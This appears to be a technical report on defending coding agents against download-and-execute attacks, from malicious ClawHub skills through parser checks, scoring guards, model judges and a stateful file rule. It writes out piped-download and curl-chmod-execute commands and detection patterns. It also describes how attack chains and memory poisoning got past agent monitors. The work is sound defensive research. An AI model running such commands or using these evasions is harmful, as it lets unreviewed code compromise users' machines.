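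The agent installed the malware in some cases, and the user did in others. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, describes skills that directed the agent to decode a command that fetched a script and piped it into a shell. The encoding hid the download address from anyone skimming the instructions. PolySwarm's *The ClawHavoc Campaign* (2026) describes attackers persuading users to run the malware themselves. A command that the user pastes into a terminal doesn't appear in the agent's history.

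Broader studies confirm that downloading and running code is a common technique in malicious skills. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) examines 157 confirmed malicious skills, some of which used the technique more than once, and finds 159 instances of it, more than of any other technique. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) reports that 34 of 82 skills with a hidden harmful purpose were malicious installers. One installer posed as a coding agent and sent the user to download a supposed driver.

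*MalSkillBench* (2026), by contrast, has 33 cases of credential theft but only 7 of remote code execution in its sample of real skills. Part of the difference may come from the labeling, since a skill that downloads a program to steal passwords fits both categories.

The instructions in these skills often called for extra software from outside the marketplace. This warning sign was visible before any command ran, and a reviewer could have asked why the skill needed the software.

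### The forms of the chain and the frequency of attacks

The table leaves out OpenHands, where the attack was the same as the one on Claude.

| Case | How the code arrived | What the agent's commands showed |
|---|---|---|
| Embrace The Red, Claude Computer Use | Browser download | Search, chmod, program start |
| Hall and Engelbrecht | DNS lookup by a script | A documented setup command |
| Forever Security | npm | A settings change and an install command |
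| Clerk's documentation | npx | One npx command |
| Lupinacci and colleagues | Encoded text in the prompt | Decoding or unpacking, sometimes chmod, program start |
| ClawHub skills | Download piped into a shell, or installation by the user | An encoded command, or nothing |

A rule that required curl or wget, then chmod, then execution of the same file would have missed every row. It would still catch the literal three-command sequence, but a detector needs to cover more. Some attacks don't need a command from the agent. Google Cloud describes a malicious settings file, linked to a known group of attackers, that leads to code being downloaded and run when someone opens the project folder in an editor. Security scanners failed to flag the file for several days.

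The demonstrations can't show how often such attacks happen. Codex's rate of over 90% applies to sessions in which the planted file was already in the folder, and doesn't measure how many Downloads folders contain such a file. Forever reports a single real case.

The skill counts come closer to measuring frequency, but they vary widely. Koi's first audit found that 12% of ClawHub's skills were malicious. By 16 February, Koi (2026) had found 824 among more than 10,700, or under 8%. *SKILLLITE* (2026) cites a Cisco count of over 800 malicious skills, close to Koi's, but puts them at roughly 20% of the marketplace. It also reports that the 157 confirmed cases came from 98,380 skills across public collections, or 0.16%.

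These studies covered different marketplaces at different times and used different standards of proof. Copies inflate some of the totals. *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (2026) confirmed 76 malicious skills by hand but counted a skill again when someone republished it under another name. It also left many flagged skills unreviewed, so the true number could be higher. *MalSkillBench* finds that most real samples come from a few large campaigns, so one busy attacker can change the percentage within days. All of these studies count published skills and don't measure how many machines those skills infected, if any.

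## Checking the text of a command before it runs

In most of these attacks the agent sent at least one command to the shell, so a program could have checked that command before it ran. The simplest such programs search the text for forbidden words. More elaborate ones parse the command, score it, or query a language model about it.

### Matching words

A word-matching rule might block any command that contains `| bash`, because people often pipe a download into a shell this way. The rule would also block `echo "never run curl | bash"`, which only prints a warning, and it would miss `|bash`, written without the space.

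A bigger problem with lists of forbidden commands is that many commands can do the same thing. In *One Goal, Many Commands*, Chen and Lin (2026) collected 1,709 such lists from GitHub, all written for AI agents. They had a language model propose alternatives to the blocked commands and tested in a sandbox whether the alternatives had the same effect. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists failed to block everything their authors wanted to. Some authors had overlooked less familiar commands, and others had left a command off because it also has ordinary uses. Repairing a list would require adding 217 commands on average.

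Chen and Lin studied only file operations, such as reading, copying and deleting, so their figures don't cover downloads. But curl and Bash are the sort of commands people leave off a blocklist because they need to use them.

### Recognising a download piped into a shell

A parser does better than a word search because it works out the grammar of the command. It produces a syntax tree, which records the programs in the command, their arguments, and how the programs are connected. For `curl example.org/install.sh | bash`, the tree looks roughly like this:

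```
pipeline
  command: curl
    argument: example.org/install.sh
  command: bash
```

The echo command above has a different tree. It contains one command, echo, with quoted text as its argument, and no pipeline. A rule that matches a pipeline from curl to Bash will therefore not flag it.

Monperrus built a defence for Claude Code on this principle. It targets the piped form because a piped script is never saved to disk, so nobody can read it or compare it with a checksum (a short fingerprint of a file's contents) before it runs.

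His rule runs on Semgrep, the scanner that Wu and colleagues used in their tests. The rule matches any pipeline with curl or wget on the left and one of ten shells on the right, regardless of the options, address, quoting or line breaks. Semgrep's own published rule covers only curl piped into Bash.

Claude Code lets users install hooks, which are scripts it runs at set moments. Monperrus's hook runs before every shell command. It writes the command to a temporary file, which Semgrep parses and checks against the rule. If the rule matches, the hook blocks the command and returns a reason that the agent can read. The hook also blocks the command if Semgrep is missing or crashes.

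Monperrus tried the hook on seven commands. It blocked all five piped downloads: curl piped into Bash, sh and zsh, and wget piped into Bash, written two ways. It allowed `echo hello` and a curl command that saved a script to a file. The test confirms that the rule works on the forms he wrote it for, but it is little evidence about false positives, because neither of the allowed commands contained both a download and a shell.

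The second allowed command is also a way around the hook. Monperrus says the hook won't block an agent that downloads a script with one command and runs it with the next. The recommendation in the hook's own message is to download the script, inspect it and then execute it. An agent that skips the inspection runs the same code as before, with one extra command.

Comparing the file with a published checksum would be a stronger control, but Monperrus notes that projects rarely publish one. An attacker who controls the page with the checksum can change it.

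### When the check and the shell disagree

Even a good parser has to interpret a command the same way the shell does. In most agents, the check parses and approves the command, and then the shell parses the same text again. If the two interpret it differently, the agent runs a different command from the one it approved.

*ParseGap* (Li, 2026) looked for differences between how the check's parser and the shell read a command in eight coding agents, including Codex, Gemini CLI and Cline, and traced the failures to 17 causes. In two agents, the parser could miss a second command entirely. More often, the parser and the shell agreed, but the check allowed a program because of its name, even though some of its options can write files or start other programs. Of the 55 cases of this kind that Li put together, the strictest agent's check allowed 9 and the most lenient allowed 47.

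Li's solution, ShellPlan, parses the command once and starts the programs itself, so the text never reaches a shell. It accepts only part of the shell's language and sends everything else to a person. In a test with ten models and no person available, none of 90 attack runs succeeded, compared with 62 of 90 without a check. But with ShellPlan the agents finished fewer harmless tasks, 74 out of 100 instead of 93, and most of the loss came from the four smaller models. On recorded sessions of the agent OpenHands, ShellPlan approved none of the 108 read-only steps, because every command began with `cd`, which it doesn't support.

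ShellPlan also won't start a program stored in the project folder, so it would stop `./tool` in both histories compared earlier, whether the program was downloaded or freshly compiled.

### Scoring a command

Most of the rules described so far either match a command or don't. *CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that instead adds up several weaker signs of danger. It checks one shell command at a time, before the command runs, and returns a verdict of allow, warn or deny.

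CARE first normalises the command, which means rewriting it in a standard form. It removes outer layers, such as a shell started only to run another command, and decodes some common disguises. In one of the paper's examples, CARE reassembles a deletion command that was split across several variables. It does all this without running anything. If CARE can't parse a command that contains high-risk words, it denies the command.

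It then gives the command four scores between 0 and 1.

| Score | What it measures | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Type, *s*ₜ | What kind of command it is | Reading a file 0; download 0.40; starting a shell 0.60; changing permissions 0.75 |
| Path, *s*ₚ | Which files it touches | Project folder 0; writing to system settings 0.70; secret keys 0.85 |
| Pattern, *s*ᵣ | The strongest match among 139 rules for known attacks | Depends on the rule's source and confidence |
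| Structure, *s*ₛ | How the parts fit together | Ordinary pipe 0.05; pipe into an interpreter 1.00 |

Some options raise the type score, up to 1. Of the 139 pattern rules, 92 come from MITRE ATT&CK and 31 from GTFOBins, a public catalogue of Unix programs that people can use to get around restrictions. Liu and colleagues wrote the other 16 and gave them less weight. The largest group, with 32 rules, covers downloading and executing code.

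The final score is a weighted sum:

score = 0.3 *s*ₜ + 0.3 *s*ₚ + 0.3 *s*ᵣ + 0.1 *s*ₛ

CARE allows a command that scores below 0.15 and denies one that scores 0.35 or more. Anything in between is a warning.

In one of the paper's worked examples, a command uses rsync, a file-copying program, to send a finished build to another machine. Its type score is 0.40, because rsync counts as a network transfer. A pattern rule about copying files between machines gives it 0.75, and the other two scores are zero.

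0.3 × 0.40 + 0.3 × 0 + 0.3 × 0.75 + 0.1 × 0 = 0.345

That barely counts as a warning. CARE first checks whether the evidence is strong enough to deny the command, for instance because the command touches secret keys. Here it wasn't, so a language model made the decision based on the command and the evidence. It classified the command as safe, and the copy went ahead.

We can also calculate scores for the running example from the values in the paper. The table assumes that no pattern rule matches.

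| Command | Type score | Final score | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| `curl -o tool example.org/tool` | 0.40 | 0.12 | Allow |
| `chmod +x tool` | 0.75 or more | 0.225 to 0.30 | Warn |
| `./tool` | 0.35 (unknown program) | 0.105 | Allow |

Of the three commands, the one that does the damage gets the lowest score. CARE would detect chmod and probably deny it without consulting the model, as it does for high-risk types of command with a type score of at least 0.70. It would treat chmod the same way when an agent makes its own script executable. `bash tool` needs no chmod and would score 0.18, so CARE would issue a warning and leave the decision to the model.

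The piped form scores higher, with 0.12 for the download and 0.10 for the pipe into a shell, for a total of 0.22. A pattern rule would have to score at least 0.44 to trigger a denial, which seems likely since 32 rules cover the subject.

### The 549-command test

Liu and colleagues tested CARE on 549 commands, 220 dangerous and 329 harmless. Most of the dangerous ones came from Atomic Red Team, a public collection of simulated attacks, and from a benchmark called RedCode. The harmless ones were mainly everyday commands from a dataset of shell commands with English descriptions. The team used a separate set of 1,313 commands to choose the settings.

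They compared CARE with other guards, including several language models that judged every command.

| Guard | Detection rate | False-positive rate | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Word matching, 22 rules | 17.27% | 0.00% | 0.01 ms |
| OpenClaw4Layer, fixed rules | 57.27% | 0.30% | 0.02 ms |
| GPT-OSS-Safeguard | 30.00% | 1.82% | 459.89 ms |
| Llama Guard 3 | 39.55% | 1.22% | 50.23 ms |
| NeMo Guardrails with Qwen3-Coder | 58.18% | 7.60% | 95.23 ms |
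| Qwen3-Coder, general safety prompt | 63.18% | 17.02% | 47.97 ms |
| Qwen3-Coder, prompt listing seven threats | 67.27% | 11.25% | 45.90 ms |
| Granite Guardian | 82.27% | 45.90% | 17.25 ms |
| CARE, static rules only | 75.91% | 1.82% | 0.34 ms |
| CARE with its model judge | 75.91% | 0.91% | 2.32 ms |

Word matching raised no false alarms but missed more than four out of five dangerous commands. Granite Guardian, a small safety model from IBM, caught the most dangerous commands but also blocked nearly half of the harmless ones. The comparison is a little unfair to Granite Guardian, Llama Guard and GPT-OSS-Safeguard, which are general safety models and not specialized for shell commands. All the models in the table are also small and old by late 2026 standards.

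The model judge contributed less to CARE's result than readers might infer from the table. Static rules produced 117 warnings and were enough to decide 94 of them. The model reviewed the other 23 and cleared three, all for harmless rsync commands. This cut false alarms from six to three, a difference small enough to be due to chance.

Liu and colleagues also reduced the lower threshold from 0.15 to 0.10. The static rules then caught 96.82% of the dangerous commands, but their false-positive rate rose to 23.10%. At 0.10, CARE would warn about both the download (0.12) and `./tool` (0.105) in the running example, but it would also warn about every other plain download and every unrecognized program, which helps explain the higher false-positive rate.

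Only five of the 220 dangerous commands in the test belonged to the download-and-execute group, which is the test's biggest weakness for this report. CARE caught four, as did Qwen3-Coder with the threat list. Granite Guardian caught all five, and word matching caught two. Five commands are far too few to tell the better guards apart, and CARE's 75.91% mostly reflects how well it recognises other kinds of danger.

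### Asking a language model

Language models can use context that's hard to write into a rule, but their reasoning can also lead them to dismiss a correct alarm. The second CARE experiment shows this. Liu and colleagues had Qwen3-Coder write 600 commands from descriptions of attacks. They had the guards check each command, then tried it in a sandbox. A command counted as harm if the guard allowed it and it ran successfully.

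| Guard | Harm | Commands blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 74.83% | 0% |
| Word matching | 72.67% | 8.17% |
| CARE, static rules only | 37.33% | 54.00% |
| CARE with its model judge | 52.50% | 38.67% |
| Granite Guardian | 26.33% | 71.83% |

Static rules alone cut harm by half. Adding the judge made the results worse because it released 92 commands that the rules had stopped, and 91 of those ran successfully. The judge was Qwen3-Coder, the same model that had written the attacks, and Liu and colleagues suspect that it missed them because the phrasing was its own. A judge from another company might have done better, but they didn't test one inside CARE.

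The sandbox had no internet connection, so commands that needed to download something from outside couldn't succeed. This experiment therefore also provides very little evidence about the download chain.

Newer judges do better, although the tests differ too much to compare the results directly. In Li's test, a judge running on DeepSeek V4.1 Flash let 6 of 90 attack runs succeed. The judge added about six seconds to each task, while ShellPlan added about a thousandth of a second.

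The classifier in Claude Code works in two stages to save time. According to Anthropic, the first stage gives a one-word answer and is biased towards blocking. The second stage reasons at length, but only about actions the first stage flags. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's employees, the first stage flagged 8.5% of harmless actions, and the second reduced that to 0.4%. The full classifier missed 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted. With so few cases, the true rate could be from about 10% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the action as dangerous but wrongly classified it as one the user had agreed to.

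The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that the agent can't argue for a bad command, and removes the output of commands because injected instructions usually appear there. The classifier can read a script that the agent writes and then runs, because the text of the script is in a tool call. If the agent downloads the script instead, the classifier can judge it by its address and the user's request, but can't read its contents.

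Anthropic's current documentation lists downloading and executing code, such as piping curl into Bash, among the things the classifier blocks by default. It also warns that auto mode "does not guarantee safety". The error rates above aren't specific to downloads, and neither is a prompt injection test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. In that test, none of 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time even without the classifier, so the test could show little about what the classifier adds.

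*Shall We Approve?* describes a system that runs the command first, records its effects, and keeps the result only if a judge approves. Besides the command's text, the judge gets the user's task, the history and a report of the effects. Its instructions say that a lack of network activity in the report doesn't prove that the command is safe, which is sensible because a program can wait before doing harm. They also tell the judge to look for anything the command has set up to run later.

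### How many alarms are right

A false-positive rate of 0.91% sounds very low. Whether it is low enough depends on how rare dangerous commands are.

Liu and colleagues give the numbers for 10,000 commands of which 1%, or 100, are dangerous (they chose the 1% as an illustration). CARE with its judge catches 75.91% of the 100, which is about 76, and misses 24. It also blocks 0.91% of the 9,900 harmless commands, which is about 90. That makes 166 alarms, of which 76 are right:

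76 / (76 + 90) ≈ 46%

Fewer than half of the alarms from the full version of the guard are right, even though it wrongly flags fewer than one in a hundred harmless commands. With static rules only, the guard raises about 180 false alarms, and 30% of its alarms are right. If one command in a thousand is dangerous, which probably still overstates the rate for most developers, about 8% of the full version's alarms are right.

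The 0.91% false-positive rate is a rough estimate because it comes from three commands out of 329. A sample of that size is compatible with a true rate between about 0.3% and 2.6%, which would mean between 30 and 260 false alarms in the example. On other collections of commands, including some chosen because they look dangerous but aren't, CARE's false-positive rate was between 8.13% and 13.04%. At 8.13%, the 76 correct alarms would come with about 800 false ones.

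False alarms matter less if the block is reported to the agent instead of a person, because the agent may only need to try again. Claude Code does this, and turns to the user after three blocks in a row or twenty in a session. In a test of 300 harmless tasks, with up to five turns each, agents with CARE solved 65.33%, the same share as agents without a guard, and CARE blocked only four commands. Granite Guardian blocked 529, and the share of solved tasks fell to 49.33%.

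### One line or three tool calls

When an agent joins the three commands with `&&`, the parser puts the whole chain in one tree. A rule could search that tree for all three steps, provided it can resolve `tool` and `./tool` to the same file.

Few checks use this. Monperrus's rule looks only for pipelines, so it doesn't match commands joined by `&&`. The code editor Zed parses a joined line but then compares each command with the user's rules separately, like the products described earlier. Anthropic's classifier is correctly instructed to treat commands joined by `&&` as a single action.

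If the agent sends the same commands as three tool calls, a check on single commands can't connect them, however well it parses each one. Liu and colleagues acknowledge this limit in their own system, CARE, by naming "staged download-chmod-execute chains" as outside its scope. They correctly note that each step still has to pass the check, but on their published values the first and third steps pass easily.

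An attacker doesn't need to plan for this, because agents often send commands one at a time. They also rephrase blocked commands. In Li's test, ShellPlan interrupted 54 runs of harmless tasks, and in 38 of them the agent changed its shell command and tried again. An agent that can't pipe a script into Bash may well save it to a file and run it in the next call, with no bad intent. Only a check that has a record of the download could identify that file.

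## Remembering earlier commands

A check can connect `curl`, `chmod` and `./tool` by recording what earlier commands did to each file. A rule that relies on this record is called a sequence rule, or stateful rule. The rule below needs four states per file and a list of approved contents.

### A state for each file

A file is unknown while the rule has no record of it coming from the network. Unknown files include the user's own files and any that the agent writes or compiles. A file's state changes to downloaded when a command fetches it, to executable when a later command sets its execute bit, and to run when the rule allows it to start.

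| Event | State before | State after | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| A command downloads the file | Any | Downloaded | Allow |
| chmod sets the execute bit | Downloaded | Executable | Allow |
| chmod sets the execute bit | Unknown | Unknown | Allow |
| A local build replaces the file | Any | Unknown | Allow |
| The file starts | Unknown | Unknown | Allow |
| The file starts, contents approved | Any other | Run | Allow |
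| The file starts, contents not approved | Any other | No change | Refuse |

"Approved" means that the file's hash, a type of checksum, is on a list. With a function such as SHA-256, nobody knows how to make two different files with the same hash. The entry can come from a software publisher, a company's security team, or a user who has just read the script.

In pseudocode, the rule looks like this:

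```
after download(file):
    state[file] = downloaded
after set_execute_bit(file):
    if state[file] == downloaded: state[file] = executable
after local_build(file):
    state[file] = unknown

before start(file):       # directly or through an interpreter
    if state[file] == unknown: allow
    else if hash(file) in approved: state[file] = run; allow
    else: refuse
```

The rule blocks an unapproved download from running whether or not chmod has made it executable. Recording the executable state is still useful because it lets a monitor alert someone one command before the file runs.

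Temporal logic, a notation for statements about the order of events, puts the rule on one line:

□ ∀*x* [ start(*x*) ∧ ◆download(*x*) → approved(hash(*x*)) ]

The box means "at every moment" and the diamond means "at some earlier moment". For every file *x*, if *x* is about to start and a command downloaded it earlier, the hash of its present contents must be on the approved list. The table is slightly more lenient, because a local build returns a file to the unknown state. To match the table, replace ◆download(*x*) with

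¬build(*x*) S download(*x*)

where S means "since". A command has downloaded *x*, and no local build has replaced it since then.

Both versions use only past events and the file's present contents, so a check can give a result before the command runs. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) describes Agent-C, a system whose rules can similarly refer only to the outputs of past steps. The paper proves that every run Agent-C finishes without an error complies with its rules.

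### The same file and the same contents

An agent might download a table of data, make its own deployment script executable and then run the project's tests, as often happens on a developer's machine. A rule that checked only for a download, a chmod and a program start would raise an alarm, even though the three commands involve three different files.

A file can have several names, so the check has to convert each name to a full path to tie the steps to the same file. In the running example, `tool`, `./tool` and the full path all refer to one file, and a `cd` between two tool calls changes what the short names refer to. The check also has to carry the file's state over to the new path when a command renames or copies it, and from an archive to the extracted files when a command unpacks it.

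Approval has to depend on the file's contents, since the server can change them at any time. If a user approves `tool` on Monday and the agent downloads it again on Tuesday, the rule compares the new file's hash with the list of approved hashes. The user needs to approve the file again only if it has changed. The check should also ensure that nothing can replace the file between computing the hash and running it.

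A downloaded file counts as started when it is passed to an interpreter, as in `bash tool`, because its instructions run whether or not it is executed directly. The rule also has to recognise Python, Node and other interpreters, and the shell's `source` command, which runs a script inside the current shell. A download piped into a shell leaves no file to hash, so it is simplest to count the whole command as an unapproved start.

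The agent must not be able to write to the approved list. *Proof-of-Execution Memory* (2026) describes an attack that plants a false entry in an agent's notes, such as a claim that it has already validated a source. The agent relies on this entry and skips the safety step. The paper's defence checks such claims against a separate log of actions that actually ran. Each log entry carries a code computed with a secret key and linked to the previous entry, so an attacker without the key can't alter an old entry unnoticed. In the paper's tests, this reduced the attack's success rate to 0% and blocked no legitimate work. A "checksum verified" note should likewise count as approval only if the log shows that the comparison ran and the checksums matched.

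### A session of seven commands

In the following session, an agent compiles and runs the user's program, goes through the running example, and installs a second tool with a script. The user's team had reviewed that script and put its hash on the approved list.

The last two columns show single-command checks. The lenient one allows local programs and scripts to start, and the strict one refuses them.

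| Command | File's state afterwards | Sequence rule | Lenient check | Strict check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `cc -o app app.c` | Unknown | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| 2. `./app` | Unknown | Allow | Allow | Refuse |
| 3. `curl -o tool example.org/tool` | Downloaded | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| 4. `chmod +x tool` | Executable | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| 5. `./tool` | Executable | Refuse | Allow | Refuse |
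| 6. `curl -o setup.sh example.org/setup.sh` | Downloaded | Allow | Allow | Allow |
| 7. `bash setup.sh` | Run | Allow | Allow | Refuse |

The lenient check lets the unexamined program start at step 5. The strict check stops it but also blocks the user's own program and the reviewed installer. Adding `./app` to an allowlist would fix step 2, but it would also let a different program run if a later command downloaded one under the same name.

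If the server had sent a different `setup.sh` at step 6, the sequence rule would have refused step 7, although the text of the command would have been the same.

The rule would also refuse step 5 if `tool` were harmless, because it checks only whether the file came from the network and whether anyone has approved its contents. Each new version of a downloaded tool therefore needs one approval, so the rule is practical only if most approvals come from a shared list and few require interrupting the user.

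### How long to remember

A sequence rule can match only events that happen within, say, ten minutes of each other. A time limit makes sense for rules that count requests, like the one in Fernandez's experiment, because the rate matters there. But a downloaded file is just as dangerous a week later. Storing a state takes very little space, so the record can last as long as the file does.

The record should also outlast the session. *Injection-Execution Dissociation* (2026) tests agents with persistent memory, in which a malicious instruction saved in one session can take effect in a later one. Tests confined to one session miss this. Removing the agent's tool for recalling saved facts reduced the attack's success to 0% on eight of nine models. A coding agent can't work without its files, so the defence has to keep a record of their states between sessions instead of removing access to them.

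Sub-agents, which a main agent starts for part of a task, raise a similar problem. If each one has its own record, one can download a file and another can run it without either record showing both steps. All agents on a machine should share one record.

Anthropic found a related gap in Claude Code's auto mode. Inside a sub-agent, the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message, so any task looks as if the user had authorised it. Claude Code therefore checks the task before handing it over and reviews the sub-agent's actions at the end, attaching a warning to the results if it finds a problem. By then a downloaded program would already have run, so the file rule needs to apply inside the sub-agent too.

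### Refuse, ask or log

Logging is a sensible first step because it shows how many alarms ordinary work produces before anyone has to deal with them. But it doesn't stop the program, and if the user's account owns the log, the program can delete it.

Asking the user for approval works only if the user reads the request. In the data that Anthropic published in August 2026, users rejected 3% of requests to run single actions but 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval. The two kinds of request differ in many ways, so the gap doesn't prove that better prompts would fix careless approval. Still, a prompt from the sequence rule could show not only the text `./tool` but also where the file came from, when it arrived, and that nobody has approved its contents.

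Refusing is the safer setting when an agent works overnight with nobody there to answer. The refusal should include the reason, so the agent can look for an approved version or leave the step for the user. Some agents will rephrase the command and try again, as they did in Li's test of ShellPlan. Rephrasing rarely gets past the sequence rule, because `bash tool` and `./tool` refer to the same file, with the same hash.

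### Policy systems that keep a history

*AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a checker that comes close to the file rule. It combines 170 rules for single actions with a session tracker that looks for seven chains of steps. One chain is downloading a script, installing something and running chmod. For each step, the tracker searches the session's history in order for the earliest action of the right type whose text matches a pattern. It raises an alert when enough steps match. The definition does not require the steps to involve the same file.

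Yang tested AgentTrust on two sets of scenarios, one of 300 and one of 630, which include many shell commands. With everything switched on, it gave the right verdict in 95.0% and 95.4% of them, respectively. Switching the tracker off didn't change these figures or the share of dangerous actions missed, but it cut the median time on the smaller set from 1.77 to 0.22 milliseconds. Each scenario was a single action and the test cleared the history in between, so there were no sequences for the tracker to detect. Yang points this out and plans a test with real sequences, but for now AgentTrust's accuracy is evidence only for its single-command rules.

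AgentTrust also proposes safer versions of commands it flags. For a download piped into a shell, it suggests saving the script, printing it and then running it, all on one line. This helps only if someone reads the script before it runs, and the one-line command leaves no time for that.

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) takes a more general approach. Its system, FORGE, records messages, tool calls and results as points in a graph, and draws an arrow from one event to another if the first may have influenced the second. When several agents work at once, the graph shows what each action could have depended on, whereas a plain log shows only the order of events.

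Users write FORGE's rules in Datalog, a language for deriving facts from other facts. The file rule would fit on one line:

```
Deny(a) :- Starts(a, f), Downloaded(f), HashOf(f, h), not Approved(h).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if" and the commas mean "and". FORGE would deny action *a* if *a* starts a file *f* that came from the network and has an unapproved hash *h*. Other rules would derive the `Downloaded` fact from earlier tool calls. Before each action, FORGE waits until the graph is up to date, collects the facts and evaluates the rules. A deny rule overrides any allow rule, and FORGE tells the agent why it blocked an action.

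Palumbo and colleagues tested FORGE on customer service, a drug safety lookup system, and two sets of prompt injection attacks. The largest attack test used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents handle banking, Slack, travel and office tasks. Every row in the table includes a simple built-in defence that repeats the user's request after each batch of tool outputs.

| Defence on AgentDojo | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks completed |
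|---|---|---|
| Repeated request only | 14.1% | 83.7% |
| FORGE, rules about each action's own inputs | 0.9% | 62.5% |
| FORGE, rules about everything the agent has read | 0.6% | 33.2% |

The strictest policy blocked any consequential action once the agent had read untrusted text, and the agent then failed half of the harmless tasks that it completed under the other FORGE policy. A rule that stopped coding agents from starting any program after they visited a web page would probably cause similar failures, whereas the file rule blocks only the file that came from the network.

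Over 15 runs of the drug safety test, agents made 40 database queries without the required approval. With FORGE they made none, and all 15 answers were still correct. Each approval held for only one agent session, so every new delegation needed its own, and the average run took 67.3 seconds instead of 59.4. Approvals tied to a file's hash can safely carry over between sessions, since the bytes are the same in each.

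The median decision took less than a millisecond in the customer service test. FORGE also raised the share of airline tasks completed from 74.7% to 81.5%, probably because a blocked agent learned what it had done wrong and could correct it.

None of these tests involved downloading and running a file. The closest is a case study with the coding agent Copilot Chat, in which FORGE blocks `git push`, the command that uploads code changes, until two security scans have covered the latest edits. As in the file rule, an approval of an older version doesn't count. FORGE's guarantee holds only if every relevant action passes through FORGE and the recorded facts are correct. The guarantee doesn't cover what a program does after it starts.

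### Learning what is normal

Somebody has to write FORGE's rules, whereas *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) derives the limits from an agent's past legitimate runs. It records where each value in a tool call came from, such as the user's request or an email. A classifier compares the sequence of calls and the origins of the values with earlier runs, then allows the call, blocks it or marks it as unclear. For unclear calls, the system checks values such as account numbers against a list from past harmless runs. If the call is still unclear, a language model decides whether it fits the user's request.

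On 5,380 recorded runs, Agent-Sentry allowed 96.4% of the harmless ones and blocked 96.8% of the successful attacks. It needed the language model for only 3.1% of decisions. On the original tasks of AgentDojo and a related benchmark, it allowed about 95% of the harmless runs and blocked 94.3% of the attacks. These tests replayed recorded sessions, so the agents couldn't react to a block by trying something else.

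The seven agents in the test worked in areas such as banking, shopping and GitHub, and called specialised tools rather than shell commands. The method would need changes before it could handle shell commands. A shell call has one main argument, the command text, which varies too much to compare with a list. Agent-Sentry sends such unclear calls to the language model. An agent that regularly installs tools by hand would also have the fetch-chmod-execute chain in its legitimate past runs, so the classifier could learn to treat the chain as normal.

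Agent-Sentry did worse on the GitHub agent than on most others, partly because legitimate work on GitHub often uses values from text that strangers wrote. Coding agents constantly use such values when they follow installation instructions, so they may pose the same difficulty.

### Models that judge the whole session

A language model can also look for dangerous combinations without a rule for each. If it rereads the full history before every action, the total text it processes grows with the square of the session's length. *Safeguarding LLM Agents against Long-Horizon Threats via Shadow Memory* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system, ShadowMem, that keeps short notes instead. Before each action, a small model, Qwen3-4B, updates notes on the user's intent and on anything suspicious so far. The same model then uses the notes to approve or reject the proposed action.

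Wang and colleagues tested this on chains of harmless-looking tool calls, using the attack method that Li, He and colleagues developed for STAC. The agent ran on GPT-5.1.

| Judge | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Full history, no special training | 62.5% | 79.2% |
| Full history, trained | 16.7% | 77.8% |
| Notes, no special training | 0% | 0% |
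| Notes, trained | 8.3% | 94.4% |

Without training, the version with notes rejected everything, which explains its perfect score against attacks. The trained version did much better than a trained judge with the full history, and used a little over half as many extra tokens (the pieces of text that a model processes). The test was small, with only 18 harmless tasks left after training, so a single task changes the last column by more than five percentage points.

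An attacker who could read the notes and the judge's reasons, and who had a strong coding agent to rewrite the requests, raised the success rate to 25%. In the successful attack that Wang and colleagues describe, the attacker gave the judge a plausible explanation that it could not verify. Such an explanation would not get past the file rule, because it doesn't change a file's hash. ShadowMem, however, can detect combinations that nobody has written a rule for. Wang and colleagues leave coding agents to future work, so this system too is untested on shell commands.

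The classifier in Claude Code's auto mode is a session judge that people already use for shell commands. It receives all of the agent's tool calls, so it can connect an earlier curl command with `./tool`. Anthropic also tried giving it the agent's explanations and the tools' outputs, but it did worse on real cases of Claude overstepping. A version without the user's messages missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for. The version in use can't always identify where the agent got a value.

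The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* reports that in 2026 tests, a chain of harmless-looking steps passed this model-based approval in 60% to 80% of runs. The tests covered three variants, with five runs each.

The file rule could flag unapproved files from the network, and a model could then judge whether the user had asked for that software. Someone would still have to verify the contents, since the requested tool could be a tampered copy.

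### What the command text leaves out

The file rule gets its events from the text of commands, which doesn't show what a script does. If a script came with the project or the agent wrote it, its state is unknown and the rule allows it. Any download inside the script then happens without its own tool call. Yang lists this first among AgentTrust's limitations, noting that rules that match text can't follow data through a running program.

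Most of the real and demonstrated attacks described earlier would get past the rule for this or a similar reason, because a browser, a setup script or a package installer fetched the code. In the test by Lupinacci and colleagues, the rule would treat the decoded program as a file the agent had written. The rule would stop the ClawHub skills that piped a download into a shell, but only if the check decoded the disguised command first.

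Some of these gaps are easy to narrow. The rule could count npx as both a download and a start, and a browser tool could report the files it saves. But each fix covers only one known route, and a script can use any program on the machine to fetch a file. Refusing to start unknown files would close more routes, but it would also stop the agent from running a program it has just compiled.

However a program reaches the machine, the operating system has to start it, and if the program is a file on disk, has to write that file first. A monitor at the operating-system level can record both events even when neither appears in a command.

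## Watching what the operating system does

A Linux program reaches the network, writes files and starts other programs by making requests to the kernel, known as system calls. In Rehberger's demonstration with Claude, for example, Firefox had to make system calls to connect to his server and save the file.

### The events behind the three commands

The shell runs each program in a separate process. It copies itself, and the copy makes a system call that replaces it with the requested program. Security tools label this replacement an exec event. The running example produces the following events, not counting the many files that every program opens as it starts.

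| Command | Exec event | Other events |
|---|---|---|
| `curl -o tool example.org/tool` | `/usr/bin/curl` starts | curl connects to example.org, creates `tool` and writes to it |
| `chmod +x tool` | `/usr/bin/chmod` starts | chmod changes the permissions of `tool` from 644 to 755 |
| `./tool` | `tool` starts | Whatever the program does next |

If a setup script contains the three commands, the agent makes only one tool call, but the kernel still handles all of these events.

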